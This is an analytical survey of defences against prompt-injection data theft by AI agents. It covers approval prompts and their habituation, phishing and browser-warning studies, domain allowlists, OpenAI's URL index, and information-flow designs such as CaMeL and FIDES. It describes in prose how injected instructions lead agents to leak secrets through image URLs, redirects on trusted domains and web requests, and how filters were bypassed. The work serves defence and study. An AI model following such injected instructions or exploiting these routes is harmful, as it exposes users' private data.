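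OWASP's *LLM06:2025 Excessive Agency* advises developers to have a person approve high-impact actions before they happen. The check can be in the tool that performs the action or in the system that receives it. In OWASP's example, an app that posts to social media asks for approval in the component that does the posting. This is a sensible place for the check because that component has the actual post and doesn't need the model to describe it. However, OWASP presents this location as optional and doesn't require the description shown to the user to come from a source other than the model.

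Excessive agency, OWASP's term for giving an AI system too much power or independence, rose from sixth place to third in the new edition of the list (OWASP, 2026). Superblocks' *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026*, a software vendor's summary, also lists human approval of consequential actions as a defence against prompt injection.

Google's advice is similar. *Google's Approach for Secure AI Agents* (Díaz and Olive, 2025) sets out three principles: agents need well-defined human controllers, limited powers, and observable actions and plans. In a passage that Willison quotes, it calls for explicit confirmation before critical or irreversible actions, such as deleting large amounts of data, authorising significant payments or changing security settings. Disclosing private information is also irreversible, but it isn't among the examples, and a developer working from them could easily overlook it. Android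 Developers' *Mitigate excessive agency vulnerabilities* asks for approval of "all high-impact operations", which leaves the same gap.

Google doesn't rely on approval alone. Google Cloud's *AI security and safety* warns that a person who has to approve every action can still make mistakes. In Chrome, Google asks users to confirm critical steps, but it also has a second model check the agent's actions without reading untrusted content, and it limits which sites the agent can interact with. The second model and the site limits also cover actions the user is never asked to approve.

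Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) gives human approval a larger role. It adapts the lethal trifecta into a design rule that an agent should have no more than two of the three features within one session. The rule treats access to sensitive systems like access to private data, and the power to change things like outside communication. An agent that needs all three features must be supervised, through human approval "or another reliable means of validation", so human approval is enough to permit the most dangerous combination.

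Meta's examples are more demanding than the rule. Its email agent can write to people outside a trusted group only after a human has checked the draft's contents, which is request-level approval at the right moment. Its travel assistant asks before making a booking or paying a deposit, and can't visit web addresses it constructed itself. The address restriction blocks a route that the booking prompts don't cover. But the rule doesn't define what makes human approval reliable, and Meta acknowledges that a user might confirm a warning blindly.

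All of this guidance says to ask the user before the action, so Notion's late prompt would not have complied with any of it. Only the Model Context Protocol and Meta's email example specify that the user should see what is about to be sent, and none of the recommendations requires software outside the model to write the description. The biggest gap comes from limiting approval to "high-impact" or "critical" actions. A developer could follow the advice, ask before every email and payment, and still let the chat window load any image the model includes in its reply, because displaying a picture doesn't sound high-impact.

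## How people respond to links, warnings and approval prompts

An approval prompt can meet all four conditions and still fail if the user clicks "yes" without reading it. Researchers have only recently begun to measure how often this happens with AI agents, but they have studied phishing emails and browser warnings for about two decades.

### Phishing emails

In *Understanding the Efficacy of Phishing Training in Practice*, Ho, Mirian and colleagues analysed how often employees at UC San Diego Health, a large healthcare organisation, clicked on simulated phishing links and whether training helped. The organisation sent the emails to 19,789 employees over eight months in 2023. Each employee received up to one email a month, from a set of ten. The organisation randomly assigned the employees to five groups. In the control group, anyone who clicked the link saw an error page. In the other four,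 they saw a training page, which was either static or interactive and covered either phishing in general or the specific email whose link they had clicked.

On average, trained employees clicked phishing links 1.7 percentage points less often than the control group. The topic of the email made a much bigger difference. Only 1.8% of recipients fell for an email about an Outlook password, while 30.8% fell for one about the vacation policy.

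The benefit was small partly because fewer than 24% of users completed the training, and more than half of the visits to the training pages ended within 10 seconds. Employees who completed an interactive version were 19% less likely to click on a later phishing email, but they may already have been more careful. How recently someone had taken the compulsory annual security course made no measurable difference. *Phishing in Organizations* (Lain, Kostiainen and Čapkun, 2021), a 15-month study of more than 14,000 employees at another organisation, had already found no benefit from training people who clicked, and the training sometimes made them more likely to fall for the next email.

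In the first month of the UC San Diego trial, 9.7% of employees clicked on a link. By the eighth month, 56% had clicked at least once. Small risks add up when an attacker can keep trying. Suppose, for illustration, that each malicious request independently has a 5% chance of getting past the user. The chance that at least one gets through is about 40% for ten requests and 92% for 50. In general, if each request passes with probability p, at least one of k requests passes with probability 1 − (1 − p)^k.

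The formula assumes that each decision is independent, which is only roughly true of people. If 5% of people approved everything and the rest refused every malicious request, an attacker who sent 50 requests to one person would have a 5% chance of getting at least one approval, compared with 92% for sending one request to each of 50 people. The UC San Diego employees received about seven and a half emails each and clicked on about 12.7% of them. If their clicks had been independent, about 64% of the employees would have clicked at least once. The real figure was somewhat lower, probably because some people clicked repeatedly.

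An attacker who sends many emails also gives people more chances to report one. Lain and colleagues found that employees kept reporting phishing over long periods, and that their reports let the company detect new campaigns quickly with an acceptable amount of work. A company can therefore benefit from its employees' judgment even if many of them click, as long as a few report the email early enough. But people can report only what they notice, and an employee whose data leaked through EchoLeak would have seen a broken image at most.

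### Browser warnings

People pay attention to some warnings. In *Alice in Warningland*, Akhawe and Felt (2013) recorded 25.4 million warnings that Chrome and Firefox showed to people who had agreed to share usage data, and counted how often people clicked through to the page anyway.

| Warning | Firefox | Chrome |
|---|---|---|
| Malicious software | 7.2% | 23.2% |
| Phishing | 9.1% | 18.0% |
| Invalid certificate | 33.0% | 70.2% |

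Most people heeded the first two warnings. These filled the whole page, so they were hard to miss, and they were almost always right because the list of dangerous sites they were based on contained very few mistakes. A certificate warning is less reliable because it appears when the browser can't confirm a site's identity, which can mean an attack or just a badly configured server. Someone who has clicked through several certificate warnings without harm has some reason to do it again.

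Chrome users clicked through certificate warnings more than twice as often as Firefox users. Chrome's figures leave out some important sites that it blocked when their certificates were invalid, and users might have been most careful with those sites. Akhawe and Felt calculated that this omission could explain up to 15 points of the 37-percentage-point gap. They also suspected that Chrome users paid less attention because Chrome repeated the warning on every visit, while Firefox could remember a user's decision about a site. They doubted that the number of clicks needed to bypass a warning mattered much. Certificate warnings took three clicks in Firefox and one in Chrome, but malware warnings took one in Firefox and two in Chrome, and Chrome users still clicked through the malware warnings more often.

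Google later tested a certificate warning for Chrome that used visual cues to promote the safe choice. In a field experiment, the design raised the share of people who heeded the warning by nearly 30 percentage points. After Google released it in Chrome 37, the share rose from 37% to 62%.

Interrupting people also helps. Akhawe and Felt describe an earlier experiment in which Egelman and colleagues sent simulated phishing emails to 60 people. Participants who saw a passive warning in Internet Explorer, which let them continue without interruption, fell for the attack 90% of the time. With a warning that interrupted them, the rate was 45% in Internet Explorer and zero in Firefox. In an eye-tracking study, none of 16 people looked at the lock icon or other security signs in the address bar during normal browsing. This suggests that advising people to hover over a link and read its address may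 not work well, because it also depends on them noticing small text at the edge of the screen.

Laboratory studies can make people look more careless than they are. In one study of certificate warnings, more than 40% of participants said the laboratory setting had influenced them to click through. In another, where some participants played a role with fake passwords, 53% of all participants clicked through, compared with 36% of those using their own passwords. Most experiments on AI agents have the same weakness.

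### Approval rates and habituation

Habituation means paying less attention to something as it keeps recurring. Akhawe and Felt found that people paid less attention to browser warnings when they saw them more often. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) cites earlier research which found that people accept consent dialogs almost automatically if they resemble familiar ones. Coding agents make habituation likely because a single session can produce hundreds of similar requests.

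Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that users of Claude Code, the company's coding agent, accepted 93% of permission prompts. By August 2026 the figure was 97%, according to *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). Anthropic acknowledges that most of these requests were probably safe, but takes the high rate as a sign that many users approve them reflexively.

A high approval rate alone doesn't show whether users review requests carefully. Suppose one request in 10,000 is malicious. A perfect reviewer would refuse only that one, for an approval rate of 99.99%, while someone who approved everything without reading it would have a rate of 100%. If users approved 97% of the requests, they would refuse 300, but the rate wouldn't show whether the malicious one was among them.

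Anthropic also notes that users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval. This shows that they don't approve everything they see, but it isn't a good benchmark for permission prompts, because users can reject a safe plan that isn't what they wanted.

A better test is to plant a request known to be dangerous and see who refuses it. Anthropic did this with 1,053 paid professional testers, each of whom worked on a coding task with Claude Code. During each session, Anthropic replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command, though approving it did nothing harmful. Of the testers, 143 (13.6%) refused. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

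The testers knew they were taking part in a study, but not what it was measuring. They were not working on their own projects, so they had little to lose and may have been less careful than they would be at work. Anthropic also had an interest in a low score, because it was replacing most permission prompts with an automated check, which blocked 89% of the same commands. The drop during the session is more informative than the overall rate, because the testers had equally little at stake early and late. The drop looks like habituation, although the testers who reached 50 prompts may have been the ones who approved them fastest.

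Many people turn off approval prompts. The Decoder's *AI agents are thriving in software development but barely exist anywhere else* reports an Anthropic study in which new users let Claude Code act without asking in about 20% of sessions. The share was over 40% among people with at least 750 sessions, according to jc-aiwiki's *Measuring agent autonomy*, a summary of the same study. The Greek Courier's *Measuring AI agent autonomy in practice* (2026) reprints Anthropic's caveat that the default settings required approval of each action. Part of the increase may therefore come from people choosing the settings they preferred once they knew the product.

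Experienced users also interrupted Claude more often, with the rate rising from 5% to about 9%. They seem to have moved from approving each step to watching the work and stepping in when something looked wrong. Watching can work well for coding mistakes, which the user can correct afterwards, but it is much less useful against data theft, because a web request can send out a password before anyone has time to interrupt.

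By mid-2026, 62% of Claude Code users had either switched off all prompts at some point or clicked "don't ask again" for terminal commands. The 97% figure covers only prompts people still saw, so it understates how much they allowed.

*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examines 290 reports of AI agents mishandling users' files and finds that user review played a part in 105. In 80 of those, the user had allowed the agent to act without asking. In 31, the prompt showed a command, such as one to run a setup script, but gave the user little idea of what it would do. The reports can't show how often prompts prevented damage, because people rarely report accidents that were avoided.

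### Supervising a compromised agent

The Claude Code testers had to spot an obviously dangerous command. Prompt injections are often subtler. In *Are You Sure?*, Li, Dai and colleagues (2026) had 303 people work with AI agents that the researchers had secretly compromised. Each person completed three of nine tasks, such as choosing a job candidate or answering email, without knowing the study was about security. One group saw a single notice about risks at the start. A second saw a reminder beside every answer, and a third got a dialog that interrupted them when the agent produced something suspicious.

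Afterwards the researchers asked participants whether they had noticed anything unusual, and counted "unsure" as a yes. Even so, the share counted as yes was only 8.6% with the single notice, 20% with the constant reminder and 25% with the interrupting dialog.

In the email task, which is the closest to data exfiltration, the agent replied to a malicious email with private information and then deleted the evidence. With the single notice, 9.3% of people noticed something wrong, and the interrupting dialog raised this only to 15%. The dialog helped much more in a web search task, where the rate rose from 9.8% to 50%, and in a cover letter writing task, where it rose from 6.3% to 40%. Li and colleagues attribute the difference to the effort of checking, since it takes more investigation to decide whether an email is genuine than to see that a letter is badly written.

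These percentages are imprecise. The paper gives two different sets of group sizes, and the results fit the set in which only 60 people saw the interrupting dialog. About 20 of them would have done the email task, so 15% would be three people. The agent in that task sent the reply without asking, so a participant who noticed the leak could have reported it but not prevented it.

Hossain and colleagues tested whether people would refuse a harmful request before it took effect. They recruited 80 unpaid volunteers through social media. Each volunteer judged 12 requests from an agent, half of which were malicious. In one scenario, a user has told the agent to send an outside auditor only summary totals, but hidden instructions make the agent build the attachment from the raw invoices. The request shows an approved recipient and an ordinary-looking file, so a reviewer can spot the problem only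 by knowing what the user asked for and where the file's contents came from.

The researchers compared four prompts, each shown to 20 people.

| What the prompt showed | Malicious requests approved | Harmless requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 seconds |
| The exact details of the action | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 seconds |
| Those details, the user's original instructions and a log of earlier steps | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 seconds |
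| The same information, organised around the action's consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 seconds |

The last prompt stated that the agent had built the attachment from raw invoice rows and was about to send it to the auditor. The reviewer had to decide whether this broke the user's instructions. Most of the improvement came from giving people more information, and organising it better may have helped further. The groups were so small that this further gain could be due to chance. The adjusted estimate was a reduction of 7.9 percentage points, but the plausible range ran from a reduction of 19.7 to an increase of 3.8. When the problem depended on a chain of earlier steps, reviewers approved seven of 30 malicious requests with each of the last two prompts.

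People also refused more harmless requests as the prompts became more detailed. This would be a bigger problem if malicious requests were rarer than in the experiment, where they made up half the total. If one request in 10,000 were malicious, a reviewer who refused 14.2% of harmless requests would refuse about 1,420 of them for every malicious request they saw. Few people would keep refusing that many. They would probably become less suspicious and approve more of the malicious requests too.

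People are also poor judges of how well they are checking. In the study by Li and colleagues, participants who were confident that they could spot problems with AI noticed slightly fewer attacks than the others (8.0% compared with 8.9%). Participants who missed an attack often trusted the agent more after seeing warnings, because they took the warnings as a sign that the system was safe. *Looks Fine to Me* (2026) studies ordinary coding errors rather than attacks. In its preliminary study of 12 people, participants could describe how their oversight slipped but often didn't recognise it as it happened.

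Tools that make checking easier can add to this problem. *Overseeing Agents Without Constant Oversight* (2026) tested ways of displaying the record of an agent's work, with employees of a large technology company as participants. According to a summary by Hossain and colleagues, participants found errors faster but had more false confidence.

Technical expertise doesn't reliably help. Akhawe and Felt assumed that people who used Linux or early test versions of a browser were more technical, and found that these users often clicked through warnings at higher rates. Li and colleagues found that people with advanced technical experience noticed slightly fewer attacks than other participants. They suggest that the experts focused on the quality of the agent's work and assumed the agent was working honestly.

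Some evidence suggests that supervision helps. In *Dark Patterns Meet GUI Agents* (2025), people completed eight tasks themselves on websites with manipulative designs and supervised OpenAI's Operator agent on eight more. According to Hossain and colleagues, supervising the agent helped people avoid the manipulation, although it also narrowed their attention and added to their mental workload. But users can see a manipulative website, unlike an instruction hidden in an email.

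### Links and instructions from a chatbot

No published study appears to have measured how often people click malicious links in a chatbot's answers or paste malicious commands it gives them. ClickFix attacks show that enough people paste malicious commands from web pages to keep criminals interested, but not what proportion of the people who see these pages do so.

The closest experiment, *I know it's not right, but that's what it said to do* (Lit, Crowder and colleagues, 2025), had only 15 participants, who were told they were testing a new cybersecurity chatbot. They used it to complete five tasks on a Windows computer, such as choosing a password and setting up antivirus software. The chatbot gave good advice for the first three tasks. For the last two, the researchers secretly switched to a model they had trained to give bad advice, such as using a password of three or four characters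 or turning off the automatic screen lock.

Eight participants followed all the bad advice, four followed some of it, and the other three followed none. Participants were most suspicious when the advice contradicted what they already knew, as the advice on encryption and screen locks often did. The advice to run several antivirus programs at once was more successful because its false justification, that one program might catch what another missed, matched what participants already believed.

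Participants were probably more compliant because they had no internet access to look anything up and were changing settings on a computer that wasn't theirs. But the advice was in plain English, and anyone can see that a three-character password is short. Most people would find a line of code much harder to judge. In the study by Li and colleagues, one agent recommended a malicious software package to people with coding experience. None of the technical professionals noticed anything wrong, while 8.1% of the other participants did.

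Phishing studies are a poor substitute for the missing research on links in AI assistants' answers. The UC San Diego emails arrived unrequested, and employees knew that their employer ran phishing tests. A link in an answer the user asked for may arouse less suspicion, so click rates could well be higher. They could also be lower if the injected link has little to do with the user's question. Researchers could find out fairly easily by placing harmless links in an assistant's answers and counting the clicks.

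### What the effective warnings had in common

Warnings changed behaviour most when they interrupted people. Firefox's phishing warning stopped everyone in Egelman's experiment from falling for the attack, and Li and colleagues found that an interrupting dialog worked best of the three warnings they tested. A message at the start of a session had little effect, and only 24% of the people who got one noticed it.

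Warnings that interrupt people work best when they are rare and usually right, as browser warnings about malicious software were. A coding agent's permission prompts appear constantly and almost always concern something harmless. An agent that asked about every web request to protect private data would interrupt people even more often, usually over harmless requests.

People also need something they can check quickly. The dialog helped with web searches and cover letters because participants could see the problem themselves. In the experiment by Hossain and colleagues, reviewers had exact details and the user's original instructions to compare. Google's redesigned certificate warning made the safe choice easier to see, which suggests that visual design matters too.

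These requirements conflict if prompts are frequent. At the median times Hossain and colleagues measured, someone answering a hypothetical 100 prompts a day would spend about 27 minutes on short descriptions, but 55 minutes on the version that caught the most attacks. Most people would soon start skimming the longer version or turn it off.

A warning that appears only when something is wrong also needs software that can detect the problem. Li and colleagues could show their dialog at the right moment because they had planted the attacks. Browsers rely on a list of known dangerous sites, but a newly written injection isn't on any list. If software can identify an attack with certainty, there is little reason to ask the user. Browsers already show a warning that the user can bypass when it might be a false alarm, and an error page that the user can't bypass when the danger is certain.

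## Blocking or checking the outgoing request

Software can assume that an attacker may have fooled the model, and stop data from leaving by controlling the request that would carry it out. trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data*, a blog post on detecting these leaks, argues that restricting requests is easier than recognising injections. An attacker can word an injection in endless ways, but an app usually needs to load images from only a few servers.

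### Blocking without asking

An app that displays no outside images can't leak data through them. GitHub chose this for Copilot Chat, and Google's Gemini doesn't display them either. How much users lose depends on what they use the assistant for. A programmer misses only an occasional diagram, but images are a large part of a useful answer for someone choosing a sofa or a hotel.

The block also has to be complete, unlike the Copilot image filter that EchoLeak got past. It is safer to remove the renderer's ability to load outside images, or to have the browser refuse the request.

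A website can send a content security policy (CSP) along with a page. The policy lists the servers from which the browser may load each kind of content, such as images, scripts and embedded pages. Before requesting an image, the browser checks whether the image's server is on the list. If it isn't, the browser sends nothing, and the data in the address stays on the computer. The browser applies the policy however the image got onto the page, so a CSP can block requests for images that a filter has missed. Unlike a complete block, it still lets the app display pictures from its own servers.

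But a CSP controls only what a web page loads. It doesn't normally stop the user from following a link to another site. It has no effect on requests from a company's servers, such as those Slack makes for link previews or those Microsoft's servers made for documents in ReLeak. Phone apps often need a separate check, and a developer can forget to add it.

An allowlist applies the same idea to software other than browsers. The list can be part of the agent's web tool or of a separate program that all the agent's traffic has to pass through. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) describes how a developer who turns on internet access for Codex, the company's coding agent, can choose which domains it may contact and which types of request it may make. The choice of domains matters more for preventing data theft, because an agent that may fetch pages but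 not submit forms can still put a password in the address of a page it fetches.

A coding agent may need only a few sites, for documentation and software packages, but a research assistant needs sites that nobody can list in advance. OpenAI decided against relying on a list of well-known sites for ChatGPT, partly because strict rules would cause frequent warnings, including false alarms, and people could learn to click through them.

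### Trusted domains that pass requests on

OpenAI's other reason was redirects. A redirect is a reply from a server that sends the browser to a different address. Many legitimate sites use them, for example to count clicks on outgoing links. If software checks only the first address, a request can start at a permitted site and end at the attacker's. So the software has to check every address along the way, as browsers do when they apply a CSP to images.

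A content security policy (CSP) doesn't prevent exfiltration if a permitted server fetches the attacker's address itself, as Teams did in EchoLeak and Bing did in SearchLeak and ReLeak. In each case, the browser enforced Copilot's CSP correctly, but the list of permitted domains was flawed. It included domains because Microsoft owned them, even though some of their servers would contact any address a stranger supplied.

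A shorter list reduces the risk. An app could load images only from a server that does nothing but store the app's own pictures. This is easier for a small company than for Microsoft, whose assistant displays material from many of its products. An engineer who adds a feature to Bing may not know that Copilot's security depends on what Bing's servers can fetch, so somebody has to review the list whenever a service on it changes.

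Blocking automatic requests can also leave the decision to the user. As PromptArmor notes, an attacker who can't rely on link previews typically needs the user to click the link. Gemini's block on images had the same effect in Checkmarx's test. To leave nothing to the user, an app therefore has to check or remove links as well as images.

### The Silent Egress experiment

In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) tested whether it is better to block outgoing network traffic, known as egress, or to tell the model not to create it. The researchers, who work at eBay, built an agent around Qwen2.5 7B, a small model that they ran on their own equipment. In every run, the user asked the agent to summarise a web page. The agent automatically fetched the page and gave the model its title, description and text. The model's context also contained a secret, such as an API key, and the agent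 had a tool for making web requests. The page contained hidden instructions to send the secret to a server that the researchers controlled.

The researchers ran 16 versions of the attack 30 times each. The agent contacted their server in 423 of the 480 runs, or 88% (the paper's abstract gives a probability of about 0.89). It never contacted the server in 120 further runs with harmless pages. In 95% of the successful attacks, the agent's answer gave no sign of the leak, so a safety check that looked only at the answer would have missed it, as would a user who read the answer carefully.

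Lan and colleagues then added defences, using a version of the attack that had always succeeded.

| Defence | Runs in which the agent contacted the attacker's server |
|---|---|
| None | 30 of 30 |
| Tags marking the web page as untrusted data | 30 of 30 |
| A standing instruction never to obey web pages | 20 of 30 |
| The tags and the instruction together | 17 of 30 |
| An allowlist of domains | 0 of 30 |

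With the allowlist in place, the attacker still fooled the model into trying to send the secret in all 30 runs, but the software blocked every attempt.

The perfect score was almost certain because the researchers had deliberately given the attacker a domain that no sensible allowlist would include. The experiment shows that an allowlist doesn't depend on the model's judgment, but it didn't test one against a permitted server that forwards requests, which was the weakness in Copilot's policy. Lan and colleagues acknowledge that attackers can use redirects on trusted sites, or legitimate sites they have broken into.

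Filters that looked for suspicious addresses, or for secrets in the addresses, also let nothing through. But the model made far fewer attempts with one filter on and none with another, which is hard to explain because a filter that inspects a request after the model has written it shouldn't affect whether the model writes it. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoided certain requests while the monitoring was active, but they don't explain how information about the monitoring would have reached the model, so these results are harder to trust than the allowlist result.

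The 88% figure is a poor guide to current products. The model was small, its instructions were minimal and the secret was directly available to it, conditions that the researchers describe as favourable to the attacker. They argue that more capable models could be more vulnerable because they follow instructions more reliably, but they tested none. The low attack success rates reported for Claude Opus 5 in 2026 are evidence against this.

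Lan and colleagues also reject asking the user to approve every network request. These prompts would remove much of the benefit of having an agent, and most users couldn't tell whether a request described as a connectivity test was genuine. A more practical design would allow or block most requests automatically and ask the user about the rest.

### OpenAI's check on web addresses

OpenAI built such a design for ChatGPT. Because the data leaves in the address, the software checks the exact address and doesn't try to judge the site's reputation. OpenAI describes the process as follows:

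1. A crawler, a program that explores the web the way a search engine does, builds an index of public addresses. It has no access to anyone's conversations, account or personal data.
2. When ChatGPT is about to load an address automatically, for example to open an article or display an image, the software looks for that exact address in the index.
3. If the address is in the index, ChatGPT loads it.
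4. If it isn't, the software either tells the agent to try a different website or shows the user a warning before opening it.

Suppose an injection makes ChatGPT write an address that ends with the user's salary. The crawler is very unlikely to have seen that address, so ChatGPT won't load it automatically, even if the site is well known. Redirects also become much less useful to an attacker. Whatever a public address passes to the next site was already in the address when the crawler recorded it, so it shouldn't include anything from the user's conversation.

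The user sees a warning that the link isn't verified and may share information from the conversation, along with the address, which they can copy or open. OpenAI recommends that users with doubts ask ChatGPT for another source. Asking the chatbot about a suspicious link didn't help the journalist in the Bing Chat test, but the advice is reasonable here because the software will also check the next address ChatGPT tries to load.

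Users still have to interpret the warning. A harmless address may be missing from the index because the page is new, or because the site creates a separate address for every search. Many warnings will therefore be false alarms, which people tend to ignore. Someone who glances at a long address can also miss the data it carries. But the software can often avoid the warning by sending the agent to another site, which an ordinary approval prompt cannot do.

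OpenAI promises only that the agent won't quietly leak the user's data through the URLs it fetches. A fetched page could still contain false information, text meant to deceive the user, or more instructions for the model.

By March 2026 the same mechanism covered the pages and bookmarks that the agent opens in Atlas, OpenAI's browser. It also covered searches and page visits in Deep Research, the feature that ShadowLeak had targeted. A separate sandbox runs the small applications that ChatGPT builds or connects to, and it can detect unexpected communication and prompt the user for consent. In most of the attacks OpenAI knows of, the model refuses to send the data, so the check matters only in the remaining cases.

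Johann Rehberger found gaps in OpenAI's first protection in 2023 and demonstrated more ways around it in later years. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, he writes that the problem is not solved but calls the new check "a significant improvement". An attacker can still learn a little from which of several permitted addresses the agent loads.

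Rehberger's more practical worry is that some OpenAI developers may not know about the check and may build new features without it. The earlier version of the check was missing from the Mac and iPhone apps. A defence that every team has to remember to use is weaker than one that all traffic passes through automatically, although the second kind is harder to add to an existing product.

### Tracking where data came from

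An index of public addresses doesn't help when the agent sends an email. The message will almost always contain something private, so the software has to check whether this recipient should get it. Some newer designs do this by recording where each piece of data came from and who may see it. Computer scientists call this information-flow control and have studied it since the 1970s.

Google DeepMind published one such design, CaMeL, in 2025. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains it with a user who asks an assistant to find Bob's address in the last email and send Bob a reminder about a meeting. CaMeL handles the request in four steps:

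1. A privileged model, which sees the user's request but not the email, writes a short program. The program gets the email, extracts Bob's address and sends the reminder.
2. A second, quarantined model reads the email and returns an address. It has no tools, so an instruction hidden in the email can't make it send anything.
3. The interpreter, which is the software that runs the program, records that the address came from the email and is therefore untrusted.
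4. Before sending the reminder, the interpreter checks the address against the user's policy. It sends the message if the address is one the user already trusts, and otherwise it can ask the user to approve.

Willison's 2023 proposal also used two models but lacked the tracking in the last two steps. An attacker couldn't have added a new action under that design, but could have made the quarantined model return the attacker's address instead of Bob's. The privileged model would then have sent the message to the attacker without being exposed to the injection.

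In Microsoft's design, FIDES, the privileged model stays involved throughout the task and chooses one action at a time, whereas in CaMeL it writes the whole plan before the assistant has read anything. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) defines two labels for each piece of data. The integrity label is either trusted or untrusted. The confidentiality label is the set of people who may read the data.

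When the agent combines two pieces of data, x and y, the result is trusted only if both were trusted. Only people who could read both may read the result:

readers(x and y) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y)

If Ana, Ben and Carla may read one report, and Ben, Carla and Dev may read another, then only Ben and Carla may read a summary of the two.

FIDES checks these labels before the agent uses a tool. One rule permits a consequential action, such as a payment, only if nothing untrusted influenced the decision to take it. Another rule permits the agent to send data d to a group of recipients R only if all of them may already read it:

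R ⊆ readers(d)

In the office worker example, an email from a stranger contains hidden instructions to send private information to an outside address. One rule forbids this because the decision to send would come from an untrusted email, and the other because the stranger isn't among the people who may read the information. Neither rule requires the software to recognise the email as an attack.

Applied literally, these labels would soon make an email assistant useless, because everything the model did after reading one outside message would count as untrusted. FIDES avoids this by putting untrusted text in a variable, a named container whose contents the privileged model can't see. Suppose the user wants to send a colleague a summary of three emails. The privileged model uses a quarantined model to summarise the variable's contents, then sends the result without reading it, so an injection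 in the emails could spoil the summary but could not change the recipient.

Some tasks depend on what the email says, such as adding a meeting to the calendar if the email proposes one. For these tasks, FIDES can have the quarantined model give the privileged model only a yes or no answer. A single yes or no is too short to contain instructions, so a policy can allow the agent to act on it.

### What the guarantee leaves out

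Willison called CaMeL the first defence against prompt injection he had seen that claimed strong guarantees. He prefers this approach to software that tries to detect attacks. A detector that catches 99% of attacks still fails as security, because attackers will look for the 1% it misses. CaMeL's guarantees have conditions, some of which matter a great deal when a browser or a user can send the data.

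As described, FIDES checks its rules before tool calls and treats an answer to the user as harmless. That is a mistake if the chat window loads images, because the quarantined model's summary could include an image whose address contains private data. Costa and colleagues note that their system can also check the answer where necessary. An app that loads images from outside addresses would need that check, a block on images, or both.

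The designs also assume that the user's request is genuine. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) explicitly excludes attacks that put malicious instructions in a trusted source such as the user's prompt. In Reprompt and SearchLeak, a link put the attacker's instructions in the user's prompt. An agent that labelled those instructions as trusted would have carried them out as the user's own.

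Somebody has to write the policies and label the data correctly. Costa and colleagues treated an email's sender and recipients as its only readers, although a recipient may have shared it with other people. They also labelled as untrusted every type of data that the test's attacks used. A company doesn't know in advance where attacks will come from, so its labels would probably be less accurate. Willison is nervous about any design that makes ordinary users think about security policies, because he has struggled with such settings himself despite two decades of work on application security.

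Even with perfect labels, someone who can see which tools the agent uses, and in what order, may be able to infer a little about the data. Costa and colleagues accept this leak because preventing it would rule out too many useful actions.

### What tracking costs

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a public collection of simulated office, travel, banking and Slack tasks with attacks that try to disrupt them. Against an unprotected agent based on GPT-4o, 152 attacks succeeded. None succeeded against FIDES with its policies switched on. AgentDojo's automatic scoring counted three successes, but the researchers inspected these and concluded that the attacks had achieved nothing the policies forbade.

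The protection made the agent much less useful. The table gives the share of ordinary tasks that each agent completed when there was no attack.

| Agent, using GPT-4o | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No protection | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Labels and rules, without variables | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

Some failures occurred because GPT-4o confused variable names or used tools it didn't need. A stronger model makes fewer such mistakes. With OpenAI's o1, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks, up from 41%.

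Other failures result from the design. Several banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and do what it says, such as paying a bill. An agent that can pay any bill in a file can also pay a false one, and FIDES blocks both real and false payments. A better model can't prevent these failures, because the user has asked for the same behaviour that an attacker exploits.

Researchers who tested CaMeL alongside their own systems found a similar trade-off. In *SecureClaw* (2026), an adapted version of CaMeL stopped all 629 attacks but completed only 29 of 97 ordinary tasks, while the researchers' own system completed 59. *AgentSys* (2026) reports that no attack succeeded against CaMeL, but it completed 30% of ordinary tasks with GPT-4o-mini, compared with 64% for an unprotected agent. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) also found that CaMeL blocked every attack but made the agent much less useful. When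 the researchers turned off CaMeL's policies, one type of attack succeeded in 138 of 141 attempts with one model, so separating the two models was not enough without the rules about data.

All three papers promote a competing design, so the researchers had little reason to optimize CaMeL's performance. Kolluri and colleagues, whose own system builds on FIDES, put the loss for designs of this kind at up to 30% of task completion on AgentDojo. The actual loss depends heavily on the model and on which tasks people need.

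CaMeL also takes more time and computing power. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) estimates that using two models roughly doubles the number of model calls, and that a task involving ten emails could take more than ten seconds. That estimate used response times for GPT-4, now an old model. The paper also reports that reusing earlier results and replacing some model calls with ordinary software cut the delay by up to half in internal tests.

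Agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen are harder to protect, because they normally decide each click from what they have just seen. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) had a model write a plan in advance, with branches for events such as a cookie notice appearing. Their agent kept up to 57% of the performance of leading models. An attacker couldn't add actions to the plan, but could use a fake button to steer the agent into the wrong branch and on to a malicious site.

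### The decisions that tracking leaves to the user

When an action breaks a rule, the software can block it or ask the user. Asking recovers some of the usefulness lost to blocking, and tracking can make the questions much rarer. Kolluri and colleagues, who work mostly at Microsoft, counted how many approvals agents needed to complete AgentDojo's ordinary tasks with the model o3-mini. An agent that asked before every consequential action needed 48.2 on average. An agent with labels and rules needed 32.4, and FIDES needed 18.8. The first agent finished 24% of the tasks without any approval, and FIDES finished 50%.

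Prudentia, a later version of FIDES, takes the rules into account when planning. It finished 59% of the tasks without asking for approval. With a different model, o4-mini, it needed about half as many approvals as FIDES (19.2 compared with 36.8) and completed nearly as many tasks.

No real person answered any of these prompts. The researchers counted the approvals that harmless tasks would have needed, and assumed that a user would stop any action caused by an attack. That assumption is generous, since most of Anthropic's testers approved an obviously dangerous command. Unlike blocking an action, asking for approval protects users only if they reject the harmful request.

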